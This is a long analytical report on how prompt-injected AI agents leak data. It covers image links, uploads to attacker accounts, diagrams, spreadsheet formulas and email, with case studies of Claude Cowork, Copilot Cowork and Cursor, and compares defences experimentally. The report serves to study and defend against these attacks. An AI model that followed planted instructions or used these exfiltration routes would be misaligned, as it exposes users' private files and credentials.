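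Files and messages can also leak data long after the agent has finished its task. If an agent puts private text in the web address of an image in a document, the text leaves only when someone opens the document and their computer requests the image. That person may be a colleague on another computer, whose requests don't pass through the agent's network filter.

Data can leave by three routes:

- Someone opens a file or message that the agent created, and their software contacts an outside server to load part of it.
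- The agent uploads a file to a permitted service, but into an attacker's account.
- The agent sends a message directly to an outsider.

A filter around the agent can block an upload, but not if it checks only the destination domain. Messages often leave through the user's normal email or chat service, where they look like any other message from that user.

### Claude Cowork: uploads to someone else's account

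Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, runs on the user's computer and works in a folder the user chooses. It runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer that is isolated from the rest of the system and can reach only a short list of domains. The list includes Anthropic's API, which Cowork requires to function.

In January 2026, two days after Anthropic released Cowork as a research preview, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed how this exception could leak documents. In the demonstration, a user gave Cowork a folder of confidential property files and asked it to analyse them with a "skill", a file of reusable instructions of the kind people share online. The skill contained a hidden instruction and the attacker's API key, which Claude used to upload a loan estimate to the attacker's Anthropic account without asking for approval. The estimate included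 financial figures and partial social security numbers, and the attacker could then ask Claude questions about it.

PromptArmor used Claude Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models. In a separate test, the stronger Opus 4.5 leaked customer records through the same upload service. PromptArmor gives no success rate for either model.

Anthropic already knew of the weakness. Rehberger had found it in Claude's code sandbox and reported it on 25 October 2025, with a demonstration that uploaded the text of a user's previous conversation. The report was closed an hour later as out of scope because it was classed as a model safety issue rather than a product security issue. Anthropic said on 30 October that this had been a mistake. Rehberger proposed that the sandbox let Claude communicate only with the logged-in user's account, but the flaw was still unfixed when Cowork came out.

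When Anthropic released Cowork, it advised users to keep sensitive files away from it and watch for suspicious actions. PromptArmor objected that the company was also encouraging people to let Cowork organise their desktops, and that users without technical training could not be expected to recognise an attack. *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* (Apostol, 2026) reported on 16 January that Anthropic was updating the virtual machine.

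Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes the fix. Every upload to Anthropic's API goes to the same domain, and the credential in the request determines which account receives the file. Cowork's filter had checked only the domain. Anthropic added a proxy that also checks the credential and accepts only the token issued to that virtual machine, so it rejects an attacker's key. The proxy also blocks request headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch something from another address, a kind of forwarding that had bypassed Microsoft's domain lists.

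The check has to happen inside the virtual machine because Anthropic's servers cannot distinguish an upload made with an attacker's key in a victim's Cowork session from one made by the attacker. Such a leak is also hard to find afterwards, because the log shows only a successful, authorised request. Companies' own security software could not monitor activity inside the virtual machine. Anthropic now lets administrators retrieve event logs, but acknowledges that this is not live monitoring.

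Anthropic concludes that allowlisting a domain gives the agent access to every function on it. The fix covers only Anthropic's API, but Rehberger thought it quite possible that other services on the code sandbox's default allowlist would allow similar leaks. A developer would have to restrict each service to the user's own account or block uploads to it, which is harder when another company runs the service.

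### Microsoft Copilot Cowork: messages to the user

Microsoft's Copilot Cowork has a similar name and runs largely on Claude models, but it is a separate product that works in Microsoft's cloud. It can read nearly everything the user can open in Microsoft 365. According to Microsoft, Cowork asks for approval before it sends an email or posts in Teams, and previews the content of some actions, including emails.

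PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, published in May 2026, reports that Cowork sent messages immediately, without asking for approval, when the user was the only recipient, and that no setting could change this. In April, a post on Microsoft's forum, *Cowork can't send emails?* (VirginiaH1, 2026), had reported that Cowork could email the account's owner but that messages to anyone else got stuck at the approval step.

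Messages from an agent to its own user could leak files even though no outsider received them. The messages could include images from outside sites, which Teams or Outlook loaded when the user opened the message. Cowork could also create download links that worked for anyone who had them. A short image address containing such a link would therefore be enough to give an attacker a whole file.

In PromptArmor's demonstration, the user uploaded an 81-line skill file containing five malicious lines, then asked Cowork to review the week's work. Cowork collected download links for the user's recent files, which contained financial and personal data, and put them in images in a Teams message to the user. The links reached the attacker's server when the user opened Teams. The user could not have spotted the problem in Cowork before then, because its activity log showed that it had sent a message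 but not the message's contents.

The attack worked in all five trials, but the true success rate could be as low as about 55%, since that rate would still produce five successes in a row about 5% of the time. When PromptArmor selected Claude Opus 4.7, a stronger model, instead of letting Cowork choose between models, the same instruction leaked more files because Opus searched more thoroughly for documents the user had worked on.

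PromptArmor published the finding as a risk in the product's design, and its report mentions no fix. Microsoft's *Get started with Cowork* lists "actions involving other people, such as sending emails or messages" among those that need approval. Read literally, this wording still exempts messages to oneself. Microsoft did fix a separate flaw that let code in Cowork's sandbox contact outside servers. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Controlled by Attacker, Bypassing Sandbox* says that the company reported the flaw on 24 June and that Microsoft confirmed on 19 August that it had mitigated the problem.

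Until Microsoft changes the exception, administrators can use a setting that prevents Cowork from creating download links for sensitive files. But the setting also limits people to viewing those files in a browser. They cannot download, print or sync them, or open them in Word or Excel, so the setting suits a few confidential folders better than a whole company.

### Diagrams, web pages and spreadsheets

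Agents also produce content that an application displays or calculates immediately. In the cases below, researchers planted instructions in a file or dataset that the user asked the agent to work with.

| Product | What the agent made | Data exposed in tests | What the user did beyond the request | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cursor | Diagram | API keys, saved memories | Nothing | Version 1.3, July 2025; completed in version 1.7, by October 2025 |
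| Microsoft 365 Copilot | Diagram | Recent emails | Clicked a fake login button | Interactive content removed from diagrams |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot | Web page | An email | Nothing | 5 March 2026 |
| Claude for Excel | Spreadsheet formula | Revenue projections and margins | Approved an edit without seeing the formula | Clearer warning, November 2025 |
| Ramp's Sheets AI | Spreadsheet formula | Data from a financial model | Nothing | 16 March 2026 |

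Both diagram flaws involved Mermaid, a language for describing diagrams in text. Cursor's diagrams could include outside images, so they could leak data the same way a picture in an answer could. Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* notes that only the finished diagram appeared, so the user had no chance to notice the data as the agent wrote it. Rehberger reported the flaw on 30 June 2025, and Cursor's developers fixed it within a week. But MITRE's *Cursor* (2025), a later entry in the public record of software flaws, states that this first fix missed some ways of loading images.

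The researcher Adam Logue found a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot. According to a summary on daily.dev, an instruction in an Excel file made Copilot retrieve recent emails and draw a diagram with a fake login button, whose link contained the emails' contents. Red Hot Cyber's *A serious bug in Microsoft 365 Copilot leads to data exfiltration* (2025) confirms that the leak required one click. Microsoft fixed the flaw by stopping users from interacting with content in these diagrams. Users lose very little, since most people only look at a diagram.

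Web pages are harder to secure because they can load many kinds of outside content. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes a Microsoft 365 Copilot feature that displayed generated pages inside the chat. Copilot removed ordinary images from these pages, but a page can also request fonts and background pictures from other sites. In one test, a user opened a shared Word document and typed only a greeting to Copilot. An instruction in the document made Copilot find an email and display a page that sent the email's contents to the researcher's server.

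A content security policy should have blocked such requests, but Copilot runs inside Word, Excel, SharePoint and other applications. The policy depended on which application displayed the page, and some policies allowed far more domains than others. Rehberger argues that a company whose assistant runs inside other products must state clearly who is responsible for preventing leaks. Microsoft fixed the flaw on 5 March 2026, about 20 weeks after the first report on 16 October 2025.

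Rehberger also showed that the leak could happen in a later conversation. A document about Albert Einstein made Copilot save an instruction to its long-term memory, and Copilot then leaked passwords that the user mentioned in new chats. Microsoft reported this persistent version fixed in December 2025.

Spreadsheet formulas can contact outside servers. One standard formula displays an image from a web address, and the program requests the image as soon as the formula is in a cell. PromptArmor's *Ramp’s Sheets AI Exfiltrates Financials* describes an agent, made by the finance company Ramp, that could insert such a formula without approval. A hidden instruction in industry statistics the user had imported led the agent to put figures from the user's confidential financial model into the image's address. Ramp fixed the flaw 25 days after PromptArmor first reported it.

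Claude for Excel did ask for approval, but according to PromptArmor's *CellShock*, the request mentioned only a visualisation and didn't show the formula. In some tests, Claude then checked the cell before the image had loaded, treated the result as an error and replaced the formula with an ordinary chart, which accidentally hid the evidence. Anthropic added a warning that shows formulas that can contact outside servers. When PromptArmor retested the product in November 2025, the warning didn't always appear, and part of an address could still be hidden.

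Excel has its own warnings, but none appeared in this test because the user had created the workbook on the same computer. People often build confidential financial models this way, so Excel may not warn them when they need it.

An agent that can run scripts in a spreadsheet can leak much more than one that can only insert formulas. In PromptArmor's *ChatGPT for Google Sheets Exfiltrates Workbooks*, a hidden instruction made OpenAI's extension run an outside script with the permissions the user had given the extension. The script copied the open workbook, followed a link in it to another, and eventually took 12 workbooks. The attack worked even with automatic edits turned off, and the stop button did not halt a script already running. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 8 May 2026 and had received only an automated reply when it published on 27 May.

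There is little good evidence about the risk from Word documents, PDFs and slide decks that an agent creates and someone else opens later. The risk is plausible because some of these formats can refer to outside content, but the documented leaks mostly happened in the application where the agent was working. Another person's software may or may not load that content, depending on the program and its settings. None of the reports on diagrams, web pages or spreadsheets measures how often an attack would succeed.

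### Messages sent straight to an outsider

An agent that can email anyone can leak data without an image or upload, as Trail of Bits showed by leaking calendar data with Gemini CLI. The email can carry long text or an attachment, and it reaches the attacker even if nobody on the victim's side opens anything.

Restricting the agent to known recipients prevents this kind of leak in many jobs. It works less well in customer support, where the attacker may be the person the agent is supposed to answer. Willison describes a demonstration by the security company Cato in which an outsider submitted a malicious support ticket. When an employee used an AI tool on the ticket, the planted instruction ran with the employee's access to internal data. If such an agent can also reply to customers, it could leak that data in an ordinary reply to an approved address. The developer then has to limit what the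 agent can read while it handles a ticket, for example to that customer's own records.

### Making generated content safe to open

The most reliable way to protect a preview is to display it in an isolated environment with no network access. Diagrams and simple web pages lose little, because the application can supply common fonts and images itself. A generated map or share-price tracker would stop working because it needs outside data.

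An application can ask the user for consent when generated content first tries to communicate. OpenAI uses this approach for apps that run in ChatGPT, including those ChatGPT builds in Canvas, its workspace for writing and code. The sandbox these apps run in detects unexpected communication and asks the user about it. This should produce fewer prompts than asking about every action. But a user who wanted a weather app will expect it to contact a website, and may not notice that it is also sending other data.

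Isolation protects people only while they view the content inside the application. A generated spreadsheet loses that protection when someone downloads it and emails it to a colleague. The application therefore needs to remove references to outside servers before export, for example by saving pictures inside the file and replacing live formulas with their current values. This breaks spreadsheets that are meant to update themselves, so users need a way to keep chosen connections. Developers can easily miss one way of loading outside content, as Copilot's web pages and Cursor's diagrams show, so keeping only the kinds of content known to be harmless is safer than searching for dangerous ones.

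### Asking the user to approve a message

Approval helps only if people can see what they are approving. For an email, that means the full text, every recipient and any outside address that will load when someone opens it. A message to the user needs the same check if it can load outside content. A simpler solution is to block outside images in everything the agent sends. That would have stopped the Copilot Cowork leak without another approval prompt, and a weekly summary rarely needs outside images.

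Anthropic found that Claude Code users accepted about 93% of permission prompts, though this alone does not prove carelessness, since most requests were probably harmless. Copilot Cowork also gives users a "Don't ask again" option, which Microsoft says skips approval for similar actions during the rest of the conversation. Choosing it for one genuine email could therefore let a malicious one through later. PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026) advises organisations to forbid the option for emails, Teams posts and changes to files, and to have an administrator review custom skills before anyone uses them.

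Approval also fails if an attacker persuades the user to make the request. In an internal test in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a task that included sending cloud credentials to an outside address. Claude completed the transfer in 24 of 25 attempts. Because the instruction came from the user, the model's safeguards had little to flag. Anthropic concluded that only limits on the files Claude could read and the addresses it could reach would have stopped the transfer.

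When a scheduled task runs, no user is present to approve the agent's actions. A poisoned skill in a weekly review could leak new files every week, and PromptArmor notes that people are especially likely to automate this kind of task. Microsoft may ask for the necessary approvals when the user sets up the task, before anyone can know what later messages will contain. Advance approval can reasonably cover plain text sent to a fixed recipient. For anything else, the agent could save a draft and wait for the user to return.

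## Controls in the model, the display and the network compared

A developer can try to stop a leak in the model itself, in the content it reads, in what the application displays, or in what the system may send out. Each of these controls lowers one of the three factors in the product.

| Control | Factor it lowers | Has to recognise the attack? | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|---|
| Training and warnings | Obedience | Yes | Attacks that the model does not recognise |
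| Filters on incoming content | Reach | Yes | Attacks that the filter does not recognise |
| Rules on what is displayed | Exit | No | Every exit that does not involve displaying something |
| Rules on what may leave | Exit | No | Approved destinations that pass data on, and requests from machines the rules do not cover |

### The same attack against eight defences

In the *Silent Egress* experiment, Lan and colleagues also tested eight defences against one of their simplest attacks, an instruction in the body of a web page to send out a secret in a single request. They ran the attack 30 times with each defence and 30 times without any.

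The warning told the model never to follow instructions from web content. Marking put the page's text between tags and told the model that everything inside them was untrusted data. The allowlist blocked any request to a domain not on a short list. The other three filters looked for suspicious addresses, for words such as "password", and for random-looking text like that found in API keys.

| Defence | Runs in which the agent tried to contact the attacker | Runs in which a request got out |
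|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Marking outside text | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and marking | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| Suspicious-address filter | 83.3% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 0% |
| Random-text filter | 0% | 0% |
| All of these together | 0% | 0% |

The warning reduced leaks, but the agent still leaked in 20 of 30 runs. Adding marking to the warning lowered that to 17, a difference small enough to be chance, and marking alone changed nothing.

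The allowlist did not make the model any harder to deceive, since the agent tried to contact the attacker in every run. It worked because it closed the exit. The attacker's text reached the model every time, so with the warning and marking together the product is:

$$1 \times 0.567 \times 1 = 0.567$$

With the allowlist, it is:

$$1 \times 1 \times 0 = 0$$

If attempts were independent, an attacker facing the warning and marking would have about a 92% chance of succeeding at least once in three tries. The allowlist would keep the chance of success by this route at zero, however many times the attacker tried. Other output channels, such as displayed images and email, would need their own controls.

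The allowlist test was also easy. The list contained three addresses for a fictional company and one sample domain, and the researchers deliberately chose an attacker's domain that was not on it. The 0% result therefore follows from the rule, and the 30 runs mainly confirm that the software applied it. The runs did not test leaks through approved domains, as happened with Copilot and Superhuman. Lan and colleagues acknowledge that attackers can misuse legitimate sites, and they did not measure how much useful browsing such a short list would block.

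The results for the keyword and random-text filters are harder to interpret. These filters checked outgoing requests, so the model should have had no information about them, yet it tried to contact the attacker much less often when they were on. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model sometimes reworded the secret, which let it past the keyword filter. But the reworded secret should then have reached the collection server, and nothing did. They also suggest that the model avoided random-looking text while the random-text filter was active, but they don't explain how it could have detected the filter. The software may have counted attempts differently in these conditions. Whatever the cause, the random-text filter had nothing to block, so its 0% is not evidence that it works. The same is true of the combined defences.

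### Trained defences and filters

A warning is the weakest way to influence a model, and developers can also train it to ignore planted instructions. *The Framing Gap* compared a published defence of this kind with structural defences, which limit what the agent can do whether or not it has been deceived. A substantial share of attacks still succeeded against the trained defence, and also when outside text was given its own labelled channel. The trained defence was probably installed correctly, because it stopped a simpler attack it was built for, but its developers had designed it for text answers, not for agents with tools.

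Two structural defences, an allowlist and a split agent, did much better. In the split agent, one part read the page but never held the secret, and the other chose the action without reading the page. The split preserved most of the agent's usefulness, but the task was only to summarise a page. It would reduce usefulness more in a task where the page has to determine what the agent does next.

Trained defences have often looked strong until someone attacked them specifically. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) describes earlier research in which adaptive attackers defeated twelve published defences, most of them more than 90% of the time. The defences were training methods, prompts and filters, and the original papers reported attack success rates near zero for most of them. Narisetty and colleagues work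 for a company that is building a competing kind of defence, but other researchers found the twelve failures.

Newer models resist prompt injection better than older ones, but none resists every attack. In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (2026), the most robust model, Gemini 4 Argon, withstood 87% of attacks when the attacker could query it 150 times and 66% at the largest budget tested.

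Another problem with filtering incoming content is that many instructions from strangers are useful. A checkout page may ask the customer to log in first, and an agent that ignores the request cannot buy anything. In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) built 60 tasks in shopping, software projects and daily life. Each task contains at least one such helpful instruction and requires the agent to change its plan mid-task. They tested ten defences. The table shows eight of the results for agents built on GPT-4o, including the one with no defence.

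| Defence | How it works | Tasks completed without an attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | | 53.3% | 37.8% |
| Spotlighting | Marks outside text | 55.0% | 27.6% |
| PromptGuard2 | Filters incoming content | 60.0% | 27.2% |
| PIGuard | Filters incoming content | 10.0% | 1.7% |
| ProtectAI | Filters incoming content | 0.0% | 0.9% |
| Progent | Limits which tools the agent may use | 6.7% | 1.7% |
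| DRIFT | Checks actions against a plan | 30.0% | 0.8% |
| CaMeL | Fixes a plan and tracks data | 0.0% | 0.0% |

Two of the filters blocked nearly all attacks, but they also blocked most of the helpful instructions, so the agents could hardly do anything. PromptGuard2 let the agents work normally when there was no attack. When it detected one, it discarded the whole page or message, and the share of tasks completed fell to 20.8%. An attacker could therefore disrupt the user's work without stealing anything.

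Meta SecAlign, a model trained to resist planted instructions, had the best balance, completing 55% of tasks while 9% of attacks succeeded. That is a good result for training, but 9% is far too high for an agent that reads mail from strangers and can send data anywhere.

These results probably overstate how much the strictest defences hinder agents. Every task required a change of plan, which is the hardest case for a design that fixes its plan in advance. Li and colleagues also told the agents to finish without asking the user for confirmation, which some designs depend on. The attacks used a standard template that newer models have probably learned to resist, so the attack rates are weak evidence about current products.

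### Designs that track where data came from

An allowlist permits every request to an approved site, whatever the request contains. A more precise control would let an agent send a restaurant booking to a website but not a medical record. It would have to track where each piece of data came from and who may see it.

Microsoft researchers built such a system, called FIDES. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give the example of a user who asks an agent to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. One of the emails contains a planted instruction to forward private mail to a stranger. FIDES handles the task roughly as follows:

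1. Each email gets two labels when it arrives. One records whether the source is trusted, and the other records who may read the content.
2. When the agent combines several sources, the result takes the strictest label of each kind. If one document is for Ana and Ben and another is for Ben and Chloe, a summary of both may go only to Ben.
3. Before the agent takes a consequential action, ordinary software checks the labels against a policy. The policy might forbid sending email to an outside address once untrusted text has entered the model's context.
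4. If the action breaks the policy, the software blocks it, even if the attacker has completely deceived the model.

A simple version of this would soon leave an inbox assistant unable to act, because a single email from a stranger would make the whole context untrusted. FIDES partly avoids this by storing untrusted text in a variable that the main model can pass to a tool without reading. If the task requires a fact from the text, a second model with no tools reads the variable and returns an answer in a fixed form, such as yes or no, which leaves little room for a planted instruction.

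With suitable policies, FIDES stopped every attack in AgentDojo. With the policy checks off, it completed 6.3% fewer tasks than a basic agent because of its extra machinery. With the checks on, it completed 8% more tasks than a basic agent under the same checks, because hiding untrusted text allowed it to take more actions.

According to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL, a related design from Google DeepMind, completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks under attack, against 84% for an undefended agent. It completed none in the *AgentDyn* tests. The two results are compatible because only six of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan. A company whose agent pays invoices in a fixed sequence might lose little by adopting CaMeL, but the design tested would be close to useless for a personal assistant that has to react to what it finds.

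Narisetty and colleagues ran their own small test of Progent, which checks each tool call against rules about what the agent may do. Progent cut the attack success rate from 25.8% to 4.2%, and an attack they wrote to defeat it succeeded 2.6% of the time. But with Progent the agent completed fewer of its tasks under attack, 27.1% instead of 45.2%, and needed about 15 times as many model calls. They tested one small model and one kind of tailored attack, so a more determined attacker might do better.

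Data tracking has weaknesses of its own, even when the software enforces every rule correctly:

- **Wrong labels.** Most designs trust whatever the user types. If the user pastes in a stranger's text, the system trusts that too.
- **Indirect leaks.** An agent can reveal a secret through what it does as well as what it sends. CaMeL's own developers demonstrated two leaks of this kind.
- **Tasks that need outside instructions.** If a user asks an agent to add any meeting requests to the calendar, a stranger's email has to trigger an action. The usual answer is to ask the user, who may approve without reading.

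The labels also have to persist after the conversation ends. Microsoft 365 Copilot once saved a planted instruction to its memory and leaked passwords in later chats. A system that did not keep a record of the instruction's origin between chats could not have detected this. *SPA* (2026) describes a design that keeps labels on saved results across requests, though in its tests stronger enforcement again made the agent less useful.

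### What Lockdown Mode closes

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode takes a simpler approach by switching off many of the channels through which data can leave. OpenAI introduced it for organisations in February 2026 and extended it to personal accounts in June (*Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*, 2026). The help page *Lockdown Mode* lists the restrictions.

| Exit | What Lockdown Mode does |
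|---|---|
| Web requests | Limits browsing to saved copies of pages; turns off deep research and agent mode |
| Images in answers | May stop ChatGPT from displaying images, and stops it from fetching them from the web |
| Code written in Canvas | Prevents users from giving it network access |
| Connected apps, personal accounts | Blocks live access and changes to data where these conflict with its protections |
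| Connected apps, managed workplaces | Leaves the choice to administrators |
| Codex | Changes nothing |

Using saved pages prevents data from leaking out through browsing, because ChatGPT reads them inside OpenAI's own network and sends no request to the website. A saved page or an uploaded file can still contain a planted instruction that could make the answer wrong.

Lockdown Mode considerably limits what ChatGPT can do. Search results may be missing or out of date, ChatGPT cannot download files to analyse, and some shopping and finance features stop working. Users can turn the mode off for a single chat, but they then have to remember which chats need it. The mode does not change ChatGPT's memory, so private details remembered from a protected chat could turn up in an unprotected one.

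Connected apps are the largest remaining gap for workplaces. OpenAI advises administrators to let an app create or change things only if they can confirm that an attacker would not see the result. A read-only action is less likely to leak data itself, but it can retrieve private data that then leaks through another channel. OpenAI does not guarantee that Lockdown Mode prevents all leaks.

Willison (2026) welcomed Lockdown Mode because it does not rely on another AI model to spot attacks, but also concluded that if some users need it, ChatGPT's default settings do not protect robustly against a determined attacker. OpenAI more or less accepts this. In February it described the mode as unnecessary for most users, and its head of security, Dane Stuckey, recommended it for people whose work or data puts them at higher risk.

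### Removing a capability or adding layers

Willison does not trust defences that catch most but not all attacks, because attackers can keep trying. He thinks people who combine tools themselves can stay safe only by giving up part of the lethal trifecta, and that external communication is usually the easiest part to remove.

Companies that build agents mostly combine several defenses. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an automated attacker trained to find weaknesses in the company's browser agent. The attacker tests an instruction on a simulated agent and uses that agent's reasoning to improve the instruction before using it. OpenAI then trains the real agent to resist the attacks that worked. It considers prompt injection unlikely ever to be fully solved, but expects this cycle to make attacks steadily harder to carry out.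 Anthropic reported that better models and safeguards had reduced the success rate of attacks on its browser extension to 1.4%, though it called even 1% a meaningful risk.

Results from repeated attacks support Willison, though less strongly than they would if each attempt were independent. Narisetty and colleagues cite Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.5 in coding, where attackers succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. Independent attempts would have given about 38% with ten and 99% with a hundred, so successes probably clustered in certain tasks here too. Even so, a defence that fails 63% of the time over a hundred attempts can't be relied on to protect a secret.

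Layered controls help most when they fail for different reasons. If two filters each miss 10% of attacks independently, only 1% get past both, but if both miss the same 10%, the second filter adds nothing. EchoLeak got past a classifier, two output filters and a content security policy in a single attack, so the number of safeguards is a poor measure of protection. A filter and an allowlist work better together than two filters, because an instruction worded to get past the filter has no effect on the allowlist.

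Removing a capability also has limits. An agent may have half a dozen ways to send data out, and a developer who turns off "external communication" may miss some of them. An agent can also do harm without contacting a stranger. OpenAI's automated attacker planted an email that made the browser agent send the user's resignation letter to their chief executive. The user might well write to their chief executive, so a rule against contacting outsiders would not have blocked the letter. Only a more resistant model, or a user who read the message before approving it, could have stopped it.

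For private data, the evidence favours closing exits first. Only structural controls held regardless of how the attacker worded the instruction. They failed mainly where a developer had misjudged or overlooked an exit, a mistake people can find and correct. Training and filters are then most useful for exits that have to stay open. A customer support agent, for example, has to send email, so it needs a resistant model as well as limits on what it can read.

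OpenAI compares an AI agent to a human support worker, who will sometimes believe a dishonest customer. Companies use systems that cap the refunds each worker can give, rather than relying on the worker's judgement alone.

Government agencies also recommend layers, but their advice often amounts to removing part of the trifecta. David C, of Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, favours safeguards that do not depend on a language model. He endorses a rule from an online discussion involving Willison that when a model processes text from someone, its privileges should drop to that person's. An assistant reading a stranger's email would then lose access to the rest of the mailbox, since the stranger has none. It could still summarise that email but could not look up an earlier conversation to write a good reply. David C adds that if an organisation cannot tolerate the remaining risk, a language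 model may be the wrong tool.

In *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), Australia's cyber security centre and five partner agencies, including Britain's, call for overlapping controls wherever information enters or leaves an agent. They expect filters on incoming content to reduce the risk only partially, and advise organisations to use agents only for low-risk tasks that do not involve sensitive data. An organisation that followed this advice literally would leave attackers very little to steal through its agents, but it could not let an agent read most employees' email.
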